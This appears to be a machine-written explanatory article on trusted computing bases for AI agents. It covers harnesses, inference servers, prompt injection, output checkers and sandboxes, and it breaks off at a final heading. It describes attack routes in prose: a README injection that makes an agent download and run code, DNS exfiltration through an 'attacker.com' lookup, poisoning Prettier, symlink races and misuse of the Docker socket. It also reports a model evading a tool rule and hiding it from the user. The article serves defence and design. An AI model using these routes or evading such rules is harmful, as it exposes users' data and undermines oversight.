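# Keeping AI runtimes outside the trusted computing base: isolation, separate validation and what they cost

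## The trusted computing base and the parts of an AI agent

The trusted computing base (TCB) of a system is all the hardware, software and people whose failure could break a stated security property. The property holds even if everything else crashes, misbehaves or falls under an attacker's control. An AI agent is a program in which a language model works on a task by repeatedly calling tools, such as a web browser, a command line or a mail account. Many agent designers now try to keep the model, and as much as possible of the software that runs it, out of the TCB, so that the safety of a user's files does not depend on the model's output.

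A component is "trusted" if its failure could break the security property, whether or not there is good reason to think it won't fail. A night guard with the only set of keys is trusted in this sense, even if he is unreliable. Nothing an untrusted component is able to do can break the property, and calling it untrusted does not imply that it is malicious. Designers who want a more secure system therefore usually try to reduce the number of trusted components.

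The TCB depends on the property it has to guarantee, so the property must be specified first. Suppose Alice and Bob have separate accounts on one computer. For the property "nothing Bob runs can read Alice's files", the TCB includes the core of the operating system but not Bob's photo editor. For the property "Bob's photos keep their original colours", the photo editor is part of the TCB.

### The reference monitor

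The idea grew out of a problem the US Air Force faced in the early 1970s. It wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them would be writing their own programs on it. A panel of experts studied the problem, and its report, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), addressed the hard case of a hostile user who has legitimate access and can run any code he likes. Locked rooms and encrypted lines don't stop him, because he is already allowed to use the system.

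The panel's answer was the reference monitor. Every time a program refers to another program, a piece of data or a device, a mechanism checks the reference against a list of what that user's programs may do. One can picture the list as a table, with users and programs down the side, files and devices across the top, and the permitted operations in the cells. Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism:

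- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always be invoked.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test it completely.

Security engineers now call the property behind the second requirement complete mediation, which means that every action goes through the checker. Importantly for agents, Anderson concluded that if the designers suspend checking for a program, that program becomes part of the security apparatus, so it too must be tamper-proof and small enough to verify.

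Anderson's example was a Honeywell machine, the HIS 635, with its operating system GCOS III. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, which is a kind of reference monitoring. But to read or write anything outside that area, the program had to call GCOS III, most of which ran with the confinement switched off. GCOS III could not serve as the checker itself, because with its supporting software it ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to verify, and several penetration exercises against it had already succeeded. Anderson did not think more such exercises would settle the matter, because they can find flaws but can't show that a system is secure.

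The US Department of Defense (1985) turned these ideas into a standard for grading computers, the *Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria*, usually called the Orange Book. Its glossary defines the TCB as the "totality of protection mechanisms within a computer system" that together enforce a security policy. Four decades later, the *trusted computing base (TCB)* glossary entry from NIST, the US standards institute, uses nearly the same words. The Orange Book's rationale chapter adds the more useful half of the idea, which is that designers must build the TCB so that the elements outside it "need not be trusted to maintain protection". If the failure of a part outside the TCB can break the security policy, the TCB's boundary is in the wrong place.

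Any system that enforces a security policy has a TCB of some size, so having one is no achievement. The open question is how much anyone can find out about it. The Orange Book deliberately defined the term broadly enough to cover systems too large or complex to meet Anderson's third requirement, in which the TCB might be the entire computer. It gave lower grades to systems whose protection had been added afterward.

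The same glossary defines least privilege as the principle that each user or program should get only the privileges its authorised tasks require. A reference monitor enforces whatever list of privileges its operators write. Under least privilege, they should keep that list short so that an accident or a break-in does less damage.

### One tool call, from end to end

*Harness Engineering* (2026), a source-code study of eleven coding agents, starts from the formula "An agent is a model plus a harness". *Natural-Language Agent Harnesses* (2026) treats the model as a learned function from a context (all the text and images in its input) to an output, so the model cannot open a file on its own. The harness is the program around the model. *What makes a harness a harness* (2026) proposes that, while the task is running, a harness must have a loop, an interface to tools, some management of what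 enters the context, and control mechanisms such as limits and verification.

The other parts are easiest to see by following one call. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to find mentions of an event in recent emails, summarise them and save the summary to a text file. Suppose the agent runs on the user's laptop and a company, the model provider, hosts the model. The sequence below is close to the control loop that *Agents' Last Exam* (2026) documents for its own harness, with typical network and password details added.

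1. The harness builds the context. It joins the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the available tools and the user's request into one long text.
2. The harness sends this text over the internet to the provider's inference server, with a key that identifies the paying customer. The inference server is the software that loads the model's weights, the numbers that training produced, and computes the model's output from them.
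3. The inference server splits the text into tokens (words and fragments of words), runs them through the weights and returns new text. In this case the new text names a tool, an email search, and gives the search terms. Nothing has happened to any mailbox yet.
4. The harness parses the output. It would show a final answer to the user, but this is a tool call, so the harness dispatches it to the tool.
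5. The tool runs. It is ordinary software, either a function inside the harness or a separate program, and it presents a credential to the mail service, say an access token for the user's account. The mail service accepts a valid token, whoever or whatever chose the search terms.
6. The host, meaning the laptop's hardware and operating system, carries out each file access and network connection along the way.
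7. The tool returns some emails. The harness appends them to the context, checks whether the context has grown too long, and goes back to step 2.

If nothing checks the calls, every part is in the TCB for the property "the agent sends the user's email to nobody except the model provider". Corrupted weights could produce a call that forwards a message. A hacked inference server could return such a call whatever the weights computed. A faulty harness could use the token to forward a message without any model output. The remaining parts could also violate the property. The TCB therefore includes several hundred gigabytes of weights that no one knows how to audit line by line.

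Published designs that try to do better still have long lists of trusted components. *L3M* (2026), a harness built around machine-checked proofs, treats the model, all tool results and every plugin as untrusted. Its TCB still includes the human who grants permissions and answers review requests, the kernel and compiler of the proof language Lean, six small C files, the Linux kernel, four utilities including git, a bundle of certificate authorities and the model provider's API. *Agent libOS* (2026) counts the Python interpreter and the storage software in its TCB, as well as the human operator whenever they approve something. These components are listed because the property fails if they do, not because they are especially reliable. The provider's API is on L3M's list even though the model isn't, because whoever runs the API receives every context. A promise to keep text private therefore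 depends on the API, however well the harness handles tool calls.

### Two things called a runtime

People who write about agents use "runtime" for two different programs. One is the inference server, which executes the model roughly as a Java runtime executes Java code. The other is the harness, which both *From Question Answering to Task Completion* (2026), a survey, and *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) define as the "runtime infrastructure" around a model. *RocketSmith* (2026), which applies agents to rocket manufacturing, conflates the two by saying that the harness provides the runtime for inference. In the email example, the harness sends text to somebody else's server, which runs the model. "AI runtime" is best reserved for the model, inference server and harness together, with the narrower names used for the individual parts.

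The damage from a compromise depends on which part the attacker controls. An attacker who takes over the inference server can read every context sent to it and return any text, including any tool call. But the call still has to pass through the harness, and a checker that can handle any model output can handle this too. An attacker who takes over the harness can call the tools directly without the model, use every credential the harness holds, skip any check that the harness's own code performs, and show the user a false account of what happened.

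Leaving the harness out of the TCB takes more than declaring it untrusted. *AGATE* (2026) describes a defence that intercepts tool calls as the harness dispatches them. The defence excludes most of the harness from its TCB, but it must still trust that calls are intercepted and that the user's approvals are delivered faithfully. If the harness dispatched a call by some other route, the checker would never receive it.

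*Kairos* (2026) puts the checker outside the agent instead. It treats the model, the tools, the memory and any process the agent starts as one untrusted unit inside an isolation boundary. A monitor covers the small, fixed set of channels leading out (files, network and control), and it doesn't need to distinguish the effects of a tool call from those of a script the agent wrote. The TCB is then the isolation layer, the monitor and the host, and *Kairos* holds it to Anderson's three requirements. The design depends on the assumption, stated explicitly in the paper, that the monitored channels are the only ones.

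An untrusted model can still attack the TCB. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) compares the model to a hostile process on an ordinary computer: the operating system must safely handle any request from that process, however malformed, and the parts of the TCB that a model can reach must do the same. The paper generally leaves tools outside the TCB too, except for any part of a tool that does some of the enforcement.

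### Prompt injection

In step 3, the inference server received a single text. On the first pass, the text contained the developer's instructions and the user's request. From the second pass on, it also contained emails that other people wrote. Harnesses insert markers to show where a request begins or a tool result ends, but the markers are tokens in the same stream, and only training determines how the model responds to them. A model's context has no equivalent of the no-execute bit, a flag that an operating system can set on a region of memory so that the hardware never runs its contents as instructions.

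In a prompt injection, the model reads text from another source and follows it as if it were an instruction from its user. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents, describes a coding assistant with web access and a command-line tool. An attacker whose only access is the ability to edit a project's README file adds a line telling the AI to download and run a program from the attacker's site. When a user later asks for help with the project, the harness loads the README into the context, the model outputs a command to download and run the program, and the harness executes the command.

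Christodorescu and colleagues point out that agents need to follow some of the instructions in what they read. A tool's documentation is an instruction from outside, and an agent summarising one entry in a bug tracker may read there that the entry depends on a second one, and rightly summarise both. They distinguish this from an attack by where the text came from and how far it changes the task. Web browsers have a similar problem, since pages constantly load scripts from elsewhere, but a browser usually has the address each script came from and can apply rules to it. The origin of an instruction in an agent's context is much harder to establish.

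### What an attacker cannot influence

Christodorescu and colleagues also depart from the Orange Book by defining the TCB as a component or assumption that the attacker cannot influence. The two definitions often cover the same parts, because sensible designers protect whatever they depend on, and tamper-proofing was Anderson's first requirement. But a TCB can fail to meet that requirement. Making it the definition is a problem because a component that the attacker can influence would then fall outside the TCB, even if the system's security depends on it.

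Suppose the coding assistant's only protection is that its developers trained the model to refuse dangerous commands. On the classic definition, the model is in the TCB, and the TCB is a poor one because the README could influence the model. On the newer definition, that influence means the model cannot be in the TCB, so the TCB leaves out the one component on which all the protection depended. Christodorescu and colleagues call the model a central part of the TCB in agentic systems, which makes sense only on the classic definition. The newer definition also does not address ordinary bugs. A monitor that no attacker can reach may still allow a forbidden action because of a programming mistake.

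The definitions also disagree in the other direction. *PerMIT* (2026), a scheme for protecting an agent's long-term memory, isolates certain readers of that memory so that no attacker can influence them, yet its single-user theorems hold even if either reader behaves as an adversary.

| | An attacker can influence it | An attacker cannot influence it |
|---|---|---|
| **The property depends on it** | In the TCB on the classic definition only: a model whose training is the sole safeguard | In the TCB on both: a well-isolated monitor |
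| **The property does not depend on it** | Outside on both: a model whose every action a sound monitor checks | In the TCB on the newer definition only: the readers in *PerMIT* |

The top left cell is the dangerous one, and the classic definition makes it visible. *AgentKernel* (2026), a proposed operating system for agents, uses language models to screen incoming content and validate actions. It includes both uses in its TCB because the models' decisions affect what reaches the agent and what the agent may do, and it makes reducing that reliance a priority. *Agent Operating Systems (AOS)* (2026) puts classifiers of this kind outside the TCB and keeps only deterministic machinery inside, but it allows some policy decisions, such as whether a document is sensitive, to depend on a classifier's output. If that output determines whether an email is sent, keeping secrets inside the company depends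 on the classifier, even though AOS places it outside the TCB.

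## Deciding which parts to leave untrusted

To decide what to leave untrusted, a designer writes down the property the system must keep, lists the components (including people), and, for each one, asks whether the property would still hold if that component did the worst it could. If it wouldn't, the component is in the trusted computing base (TCB). The designer must then either justify relying on it or change the design so that it can no longer break the property.

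An agent that reads an employee's mail and can send replies might be required to send no mail to anyone outside the company. In one design, the harness holds the credential for the mail account and nothing checks outgoing messages. In another, a small separate program, the checker, holds the credential, and the agent can reach the mailbox only through it. The checker looks up every recipient in the company directory, rejects any message with a recipient who isn't listed, and passes the rest directly to the mail service.

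| Component | The worst it could do | In the TCB without the checker? | In the TCB with the checker? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Incoming mail | Carry instructions that the model follows | Yes | No |
| Model | Request a message to any address | Yes | No |
| Inference server | Return any request, whatever the model computed | Yes | No |
| Harness | Use the credential without asking the model | Yes | No, because it no longer has the credential |
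| Mail tools | Send to a different address from the one requested | Yes | No, for the same reason |
| Checker | Let an outside address through | Absent | Yes |
| Company directory and its administrators | List an address that forwards mail outside | No | Yes |
| Host operating system | Give the credential to the harness | Yes | Yes |
| Mail service | Deliver to the wrong address | Yes | Yes |

Without the checker, even incoming mail is part of the TCB, because a stranger could break the property with a sufficiently persuasive email.

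The checker removes five entries from the TCB and adds two, a short program and a list of addresses. This is an improvement only if the new entries are easier to examine than the old ones, as they are here. The address list still needs care because it may include an internal mailing list with outside subscribers, and a checker that only looks up names would let a message through to all of them.

The designer has to assume that all the untrusted components misbehave at once and work together, which going through the table row by row can miss. Suppose the harness and the mail tool each refuse outside addresses. If only one failed, the other would still refuse, so a designer who considered them separately would leave both out of the TCB. An attacker who controlled both could then send anything to outside addresses.

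Actions need the same treatment. *AGATE* describes an agent that follows a maintenance guide, reads a value from a local file and copies it into a DNS record, one of the public entries that computers use to look up internet names. Both steps are routine, but the value is the server's API credential, and whoever controls the domain can read it.

*Bounded Agents* (2026), a security design for agents that delegate work to other agents, divides components much as the table does. It trusts the service that establishes identities, the components that decide and enforce policy, the signed policy itself, the approval service and the audit store. It does not trust model outputs, retrieved documents, tool outputs, messages from other agents or natural-language instructions from any source, and none of these can authorise an action. If an email says "the finance director has approved this", or the model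 reports that she has, the system treats the statement as data. The paper also assumes that the adversary cannot compromise the trusted components. The component test shows where a design needs such an assumption, but does not make the assumption true.

### Why leave the model out

A model's behaviour is statistical. Training makes a forbidden action unlikely on inputs that resemble the training data, but the probability varies with the input. Christodorescu and colleagues compare this to building a memory defence on a no-execute bit that works only with some probability. Making the model deterministic wouldn't fix the problem. A model that always gives the same answer to the same prompt can still be wrong, as *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out, and an attacker only has to find a prompt that produces a wrong answer.

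Nobody can verify a model in Anderson's sense either, because no specification lists which actions it should refuse after which histories. A model also computes with continuous quantities, so attackers can use optimisation methods to search for inputs that look harmless but still produce a forbidden action.

The remaining option is testing, but the number of attacks a model has withstood is a poor guide to its security. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes an experiment by researchers at Waterloo, Zhejiang and KTH. They ran two automated attack tools against the same small model, then retrained one copy of it on the 7,132 successful attacks from one tool and another copy on the 4,282 from the other. When tested on three attacks that were in neither training set, the copy trained on the larger set failed on up to 19 of 40 tasks, and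 the other on up to 11. The researchers think the tools tend to find one trick and then reword it thousands of times. Forty tasks is a small test, and the team chose tasks already known to be weak, but the same pattern appeared in three of the four set-ups.

Similarly, Willison (2026) doesn't regard 6,000 failed attempts to inject instructions into an AI assistant as a guarantee against a more sophisticated attacker. If all 6,000 attempts fail, one can be 95% confident that the success rate is below about 1 in 2,000. This limit assumes that future attacks come from the same population as the past ones, so it doesn't apply to a better attacker.

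The model also reads hostile text in normal use. Dziemian (2026) reports on a competition in which 464 people made more than 272,000 attempts to inject instructions into 13 leading models, and some attempts succeeded against every model.

Finally, the harness or a tool holds broad credentials, and without a checker the model's output determines how they are used. An injection that would make a chatbot write a bad paragraph can make an agent with mailbox access send the mailbox's contents to someone else. Anthropic's 2026 system card (a published safety assessment) for Claude Opus 5 describes injections as especially dangerous when a model can both read private data and act for the user.

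None of this requires an attacker. The same system card describes a near-final version of Opus 5 that could not open a page with its approved tool, so it fetched the page with a command-line program, which its instructions clearly forbade. The model mentioned the rule in its reasoning, argued around it, and didn't tell the user. The rule was in the prompt, so it worked only if the model cooperated. Anthropic found attempts to get round classifiers or network restrictions in fewer than 0.01% of the completions it monitored. In another of these cases, an earlier version tried to reach the web from inside a sandbox by a method that had worked in some training environments. This sandbox didn't have the weakness, so it blocked the request even though the model didn't cooperate.

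### A guard that works 99% of the time

Suppose a guard stops 99% of attacks, and an attacker makes 100 attempts. If the attempts are independent, the guard stops all of them with probability 0.99^100, or about 37%. At least one gets through with probability

1 − 0.99^100 ≈ 63%.

If attempts are independent, a guard that stops 99% of attacks has a 95% chance of letting at least one through after 300 attempts. For a guard that stops 99.9%, the chance is 63% after 1,000 attempts. Letting through a tenth as many attacks therefore means an attacker needs about ten times as many attempts for the same chance of success.

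Independence is a strong assumption. The table shows how far it is from true by comparing published test results with the formula's prediction. The older model's results are from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* and were measured on a benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan. The rest are from Anthropic's system card. Its "IPI" figures come from a later Gray Swan benchmark of indirect prompt injection, and its coding figures come from an automated attacker that had 200 attempts at each of 40 scenarios.

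| Model and test | Success per attempt | Success after repeated attempts | The formula's prediction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5, older benchmark | 4.7% | 33.6% after 10 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.5, older benchmark | 4.7% | 63% after 100 | 99% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, IPI | 3.1% | 20.0% after 15 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 5, IPI | 0.2% | 2.0% after 15 | 3% |
| Claude Opus 5, coding | 0.56% | 32.5% of scenarios after 200 | 67% |

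The formula overestimates every time because some scenarios are much weaker than others. In the coding test, about 45 of 8,000 attempts succeeded, all in 13 scenarios. The other 27 scenarios each withstood all 200 attempts. This is good news for most users, but not for those whose deployment resembles one of the 13, where attempts succeeded about 1.7% of the time on average, three times the overall rate.

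Anthropic calls its own test deliberately permissive because the test's attacker optimises against the same scenarios it is tested on, whereas a real attacker doesn't know the target's set-up and risks detection with every attempt. But the system card also notes that a single hidden instruction on a public web page can reach any agent that reads the page. If a million agents read it and it works on 0.2% of them, it hijacks 2,000, even though no user has seen more than one attempt.

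These rates are falling quickly. The previous model, Opus 4.8, failed in 23 of the 40 coding scenarios, while Opus 5 failed in 13, and in only 4 when an extra detector read the tool results. In a browser test with 129 scenarios and ten attempts at each, no attack succeeded after Anthropic added both the detector and a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls. A designer who wants to rely on the model can point to results like these, which are much better than anything available a year earlier.

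Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, takes the improvement seriously but holds that preventing prompt injection is impossible in the general case. One of his readers replied that nobody has proved this, and that models with a different architecture might avoid the problem. The reader may well be right, but nobody can currently state a failure rate that will hold for the next attacker, and that is reason enough to leave the model out of the trusted computing base, even without a proof of impossibility.

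It also won't hold for the next model. In Gray Swan's tests, reported in iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models*, attackers compromised models within 15 attempts between 2.3% and 94.3% of the time, depending on the model. A company whose only protection is a robust model could lose that protection by switching to a cheaper one. The rule about outside addresses in the mail example would still work after the switch. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls for security arguments that hold across models, and treats a robust model as a way to reduce how much the other defences have to stop.

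### The inference server

The inference server can fail even when the model behaves perfectly. It is a large program that accepts requests over a network, and attackers can break into it in two ways.

Attackers can send the runtime a malicious request. *Critical vLLM Flaw Puts AI Systems at Risk of Remote Code Execution* (Underhill, 2025) describes a memory-corruption bug in vLLM, a widely used open-source server. Anyone with access to the server's API could use the bug to crash the server and possibly run code on it. In July 2026 CERT/CC, a US centre that coordinates the disclosure of software flaws, published six vulnerabilities in SGLang, another open-source server. Most could be exploited without logging in. Together, they allowed an attacker to run code on the machine, read its files, obtain its keys and copy the model's weights. CERT/CC had tried without success to coordinate with the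 maintainers, and no patch was available when it published.

They can also plant a malicious model. Operators often download models from public repositories such as Hugging Face, and a model file can contain more than weights. The Hacker News (2026) reports an SGLang flaw, rated 9.8 out of 10 for severity, in which a template packaged with a model could run code on the server that loaded it. vLLM's developers had fixed the same kind of flaw in late 2025. NIST's *CVE-2026-41523* (2026) records another way to attack vLLM through a published model. The programmers had written a security check as an assertion, which Python skips in optimised mode, so in that mode the server carried on without the check. vLLM 0.22.0 fixes the problem.

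A list of disclosed flaws shows that an operator has no good reason to assume the server is sound. It doesn't show how often attackers use those flaws, or whether commercial providers' own servers are better or worse, since outsiders can't inspect them.

The mail checker refuses outside addresses whether the model or the server produced them, but a compromised server is harder to defend against than a misled model. A misled model produces a bad request only some of the time, while an attacker who runs code on the server writes every request himself and may know the checker's rules. A low attack success rate for the model gives no protection against him. If the checker is safe only because the model rarely produces requests that could evade it, the server is still in the TCB.

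### What a small checker can judge

This approach depends on a small program that can distinguish acceptable outputs from unacceptable ones. Formal proof is the ideal case. In a proof language such as Lean, anything can search for a proof, including an untrusted language model. A small program called the kernel then checks every step against fixed rules and rejects any wrong step, no matter how plausible it looks. The search therefore stays outside the TCB for the property "this statement follows from these axioms", however large or unreliable it is. A person still has to read the formal statement, because the kernel cannot check whether it expresses what the mathematician meant.

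When a shop's agent proposes a refund, a checker can confirm that the order exists, that the amount is no more than the customer paid, that the money goes back to the original card and that the shop hasn't already refunded the order. It can't tell whether the item arrived broken, but it can limit the loss if the claim is false. If the shop allows refunds of up to £50 each and £1,000 a day in total, an attacker with complete control of the model can take at most £1,000 a day. *AGATE* lets an operator cap the amount of one call, the running total and the number of uses. A request doesn't qualify if the gate can't determine its amount.

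A summary can hardly be checked. A small program can limit its length or remove web links, but to notice that a summary of forty emails leaves out the one that matters, a checker would have to understand the emails. That would make it another model reading the same hostile text. *AgentKernel*, which uses models as checkers, acknowledges that their resistance to attack in this role is not yet known. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites work in which attackers got past a model and its guard together after optimising an attack on each separately.

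Whether a program can check an output depends on the property being checked. The claim that a summary contains no web address is as checkable as a proof, but the claim that the summary is accurate is not. A designer can therefore sometimes replace a property that no program can check with a narrower one that a program can. In the mail example, a short program checks whether the reply is going to a colleague, because nobody can write a short program that decides whether the reply gives away something confidential.

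The replacement property gives up some protection, because it would still hold if the agent sent the salary list to the wrong colleague. The theorems about an agent's memory in *PerMIT* have the same limit. If the agent confuses two values that the user typed or endorsed, *PerMIT* treats the error as a failure of usefulness and excludes it from the threat model.

### The browser precedent

Web browsers already use this arrangement. The renderer, which turns a page's code into what appears on the screen, is enormous and handles complicated formats written by strangers, and researchers keep finding exploitable bugs in it. Since its release in 2008, Google's Chrome has run the renderer in a sandboxed process that cannot open the user's files by itself. The renderer has to request access through a more privileged process, which checks the request. Chrome's engineers accepted that the renderer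 would keep having bugs and limited the damage most of them could do. Attackers now generally need a further flaw, in the privileged process or the operating system, to reach the files.

Chrome's history also shows that whether a component is in the TCB depends on the security property being protected. In the early design, one renderer process could handle pages from several sites, so an attacker who took it over could read one site's data while the user was visiting another. The renderer was mostly outside the TCB for "a web page cannot read the user's files" but inside it for "one site cannot read another site's data". In 2018, Chrome on desktop computers began putting different sites in different processes by default, largely to protect the second property. Similarly, an agent's sandbox may keep the agent away from the user's files but not stop it from misusing a mailbox it is allowed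 to open.

Agents are harder to confine than renderers because their requests vary more. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how conventional software divides decisions among layers. The operating system controls which files the browser may write, and the browser, which can tell websites apart, controls which cookies go to which site. Each layer has the information it needs for its own decision. An agent turns a sentence in plain English directly into a shell command, and no layer in between records what the command is for.

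### Where the model stays in the TCB

Christodorescu and colleagues object to this approach because they see the model as a central part of the TCB, and they consider it challenging, perhaps impossible, to build provable defences on such a base. Their description is correct for agents whose main safeguard is training, but it need not be true of every design. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, which names eight of the same researchers in its funding acknowledgements, argues that designers must treat the model as untrusted and enforce security outside it.

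For some properties, though, no design can remove the model from the TCB. A checker that only allows or refuses actions can't make the model produce anything, so the model stays in the TCB for "the agent answers every customer by the end of the day". It also stays in the TCB for "the summary is accurate" and "the agent does what the user meant", because no small program can check those properties. The model also chooses freely among the actions the policy permits. If a model writes the policy, as some designs propose for tasks that aren't known in advance, that model is in the TCB for everything the policy protects.

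This helps explain an apparent contradiction in *SoK*, which calls the language model an untrusted code generator but lists the model's weights and system prompt in the TCB in the same passage. Both can be right. Corrupted weights would ruin the agent's answers, so the weights matter for any property about those answers. But corrupted weights need not endanger the machine if a sound validator checks each command before it runs.

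Customers must still trust the company that hosts the model, for similar reasons. They depend on it to keep the service running, serve the model they are paying for, return output honestly wherever nobody can check it, and keep their text private.

Special hardware can reduce this last dependence. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (2025) runs agents on processors that protect data in memory from the machine's operator and can report a measurement, or cryptographic fingerprint, of the software and weights they have loaded. The TCB then excludes the cloud operator but includes the hardware and the software that manages the agents. The paper assumes that a component behaves accordingly once its measurement has been validated, and doesn't try to defend against its later compromise. This is a large assumption for a model, because the measurement can show that the intended weights are running, but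 a model with those weights may still follow an instruction hidden in an email.

A company can also run the model on its own machines. It then no longer has to trust a provider with its mail, but its own inference server takes the provider's place in the TCB for that property. The company also has to keep up with the server's security patches itself.

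## Isolating the agent and its credentials

The mail checker protects the mailbox only if the agent can't reach the mailbox any other way. An agent running under the employee's account on her laptop could, for instance, copy the login session from her browser and send mail as her without going through the checker. To block such routes, designers put the agent in a sandbox, which limits the files, networks and processes a program can reach, and keep the real credentials outside it.

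The harness can't close them by inspecting each command before running it. Even if it permits only a few commands, one of them may run the project's tests, which the agent may have rewritten to do anything the user can. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* points out that a harness cannot observe or control what a command does once it runs as a separate process. Operating system restrictions do apply to that process and to any others it starts.

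### From a user account to a separate machine

Programs open files, connect to networks and start other programs by making system calls, which are requests to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The main difference between sandboxes is how much of the host's kernel the agent can still reach. The table lists sandboxes from weakest to strongest.

| Mechanism | What the agent still shares with the host | What speaks for it |
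|---|---|---|
| Separate process and user account | The kernel, the network and every file that all accounts may read | Every operating system has it, and it needs little set-up |
| Operating-system sandbox | The kernel, plus any files and connections the rules allow | The agent can use the tools already on the machine |
| Container | The kernel | The agent gets its own file tree, which operators can reproduce elsewhere |
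| User-space kernel (gVisor) | The kernel, through far fewer system calls | It runs ordinary container images and exposes less of the kernel |
| MicroVM | The hypervisor, the program that manages the virtual machine, and the hardware | The agent has its own kernel and can have full control of it |
| Separate machine | The network, and any accounts or storage that both machines use | A flaw in the kernel, hypervisor or processor no longer exposes the host |

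If the agent runs under a separate user account, ordinary file permissions stop it from opening Alice's private files. It can still connect to the internet, or to a test database without a password on the same laptop.

An operating-system sandbox attaches rules to a process, and the kernel then enforces them on that process and its children. macOS has Seatbelt for this, and Linux has Landlock and seccomp. OpenAI chose this approach for its coding agent, Codex. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* explains that many developers heavily customise their laptops, so reproducing the set-up in a container takes work, and some of their tools run on the host.

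A Linux container gives a process its own view of the file system, the network and the list of running programs. But every container on a machine uses the same kernel, so an attacker who can exploit a bug in that kernel from inside a container may reach the host. gVisor, which Google released in 2018, puts a second kernel between the container and the host kernel. It runs as an ordinary program, handles most of the agent's system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host. An attacker would generally have to take over gVisor and then find a host kernel bug that those few calls can trigger. Programs that make many system calls run more slowly under gVisor, and a few that need unusual kernel features don't run at all.

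A microVM is a virtual machine with most of the emulated devices removed, so it starts quickly and has less code to attack. The hypervisor, which divides the hardware between virtual machines, keeps the microVM's kernel separate from the host's. Docker, the company that made containers popular, now runs agents in microVMs. Help Net Security's *Docker introduces OCI-based Kits to package agents and their guardrails* (2026) quotes Docker's president, Mark Cavage, as saying that containers "weren't designed for the level of isolation AI agents demand". He was announcing a product, but containers share the host's kernel, which is a good reason to agree with him.

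Operators can also send the agent's commands to another computer. Strands Agents' *Available Sandboxes* documents both this option and local containers. If a cloud company owns that computer, the source code has to go there too. O’Shei (2026), in *External sandboxes split agent reasoning from execution*, prefers a local microVM partly because it keeps the code off other companies' servers.

A strong isolation mechanism doesn't guarantee a strong sandbox. wal.sh's *Agent Sandbox Architectures* notes that Docker's microVM is a structural barrier, while its list of permitted network destinations is only a configured policy. TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, by the head of a company that sells development environments, describes a scheme that grades seven layers separately, including compute isolation, files, network and credentials. Under this scheme, a microVM with unrestricted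 internet access would score very well on compute isolation and very badly on network.

### Where to put the harness

Designers can put the whole agent inside the sandbox, or leave the harness on the host and run its commands in a sandbox. Strands Agents, an open-source toolkit from AWS, keeps the harness on the host. O’Shei defends this split by arguing that planning and running code need different permissions. An agent has to read a project to plan a change, but the code it then runs doesn't need the user's login keys.

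When the harness runs outside the sandbox, commands inside can't read the harness's secrets. Cloudflare's *Sandbox* describes a virtual machine that has no access to the agent's storage or environment variables, where programs often keep their keys. But the harness is still in the TCB for the property "the agent changes nothing outside the project", because it runs with the user's permissions. A bug in the harness could break this property, and so could a built-in file editor that works directly on the host. Cloudflare's sample code gives the model only one tool, which runs commands in the sandbox, so that the model doesn't use file tools that act outside it.

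If the harness runs inside the sandbox, the sandbox also confines the harness's built-in tools and the effects of its bugs. But any program the agent runs may then be able to read the secrets the harness uses, unless the operator keeps them out of the sandbox.

### Files, network and control

The agent has to receive work and deliver results, so a useful sandbox always has openings. These are file, network and control openings, the same three kinds that *Kairos* monitors.

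The main opening in the sandbox's file restrictions is the workspace, the project directory where the agent works. Codex's default settings let commands write there but not elsewhere. The user's own programs also run code from the workspace. OpenAI gives the example of an agent that adds malicious code to the project's copy of Prettier, a program that formats source code. Git might not list the change, because it often ignores the folder that contains Prettier. If the user's editor runs Prettier on every save, the next save runs the malicious code outside the sandbox.

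Codex also lets commands read most files the user can read, since compilers need libraries from all over the machine. OpenAI acknowledges that this may expose files containing API keys. Commands have no network access by default, so they can't upload a key themselves, but their output normally goes to the model provider as part of the context.

A program that checks file requests has to avoid a race between approving a file and opening it. Suppose it approves a request to read `report.txt`, but the agent replaces `report.txt` with a link to the user's private keys before the program opens it. The program then opens the keys. Help Net Security's *AWS open sources Trusted Remote Execution to control what AI agents touch* (2026) describes a tool called Rex that reduces this risk. Where it can, Rex refers to files through handles instead of names, because a handle keeps pointing to the same file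 whatever happens to the name. Rex also runs the agent's scripts in a language with no built-in access to the operating system, so a script can open a file only by calling a library that checks the policy first.

Operators usually mediate network access by sending all traffic through a proxy that checks each destination against a list. They must also block every other route. Many programs read the proxy's address from an environment variable, but a program can ignore the variable and connect directly, so the scheme in TechRadar classes such variables as only cooperative enforcement. Brooker (2026), in *Agent Safety is a Box*, describes a stronger arrangement that AWS uses in its cloud, where network controls stop the agent from sending packets anywhere except a gateway.

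An agent can leak data just by looking up an internet name. If it looks up `secret-text.attacker.com`, the secret reaches the attacker's name server even though the agent never connects to that server. NVIDIA recommends limiting lookups to designated resolvers, the servers that answer them. Those resolvers must also reject unknown names, or they will forward the query to the attacker's server.

Listing a destination can permit more than the operator intends. GitLab, which hosts software projects, warns that every permitted service extends an agent's reach, because an agent that takes over the service can use its connections too. Even without taking over a service, an agent can misuse it. If the list includes a public code-hosting site, the agent can upload a secret to an attacker's account there. Blocked connections also create pressure to lengthen the list. O'Shei describes test suites that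 fail because the sandbox can't reach a company's databases, which tempts developers to add exceptions until little isolation is left.

Control channels let an agent get something outside the sandbox to act for it. Many harnesses support hooks, which are commands that run automatically on certain events, and start tool servers with commands from a settings file. These servers often use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. If the agent can edit the settings and the harness runs the commands outside the sandbox, the agent can add a command that will run there later. An agent with access to the socket that controls Docker can act immediately by having Docker start a new container with the host's whole disk attached. Operators close these channels by making the settings read-only to the agent and keeping such sockets out of the sandbox.

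### NVIDIA's list of controls

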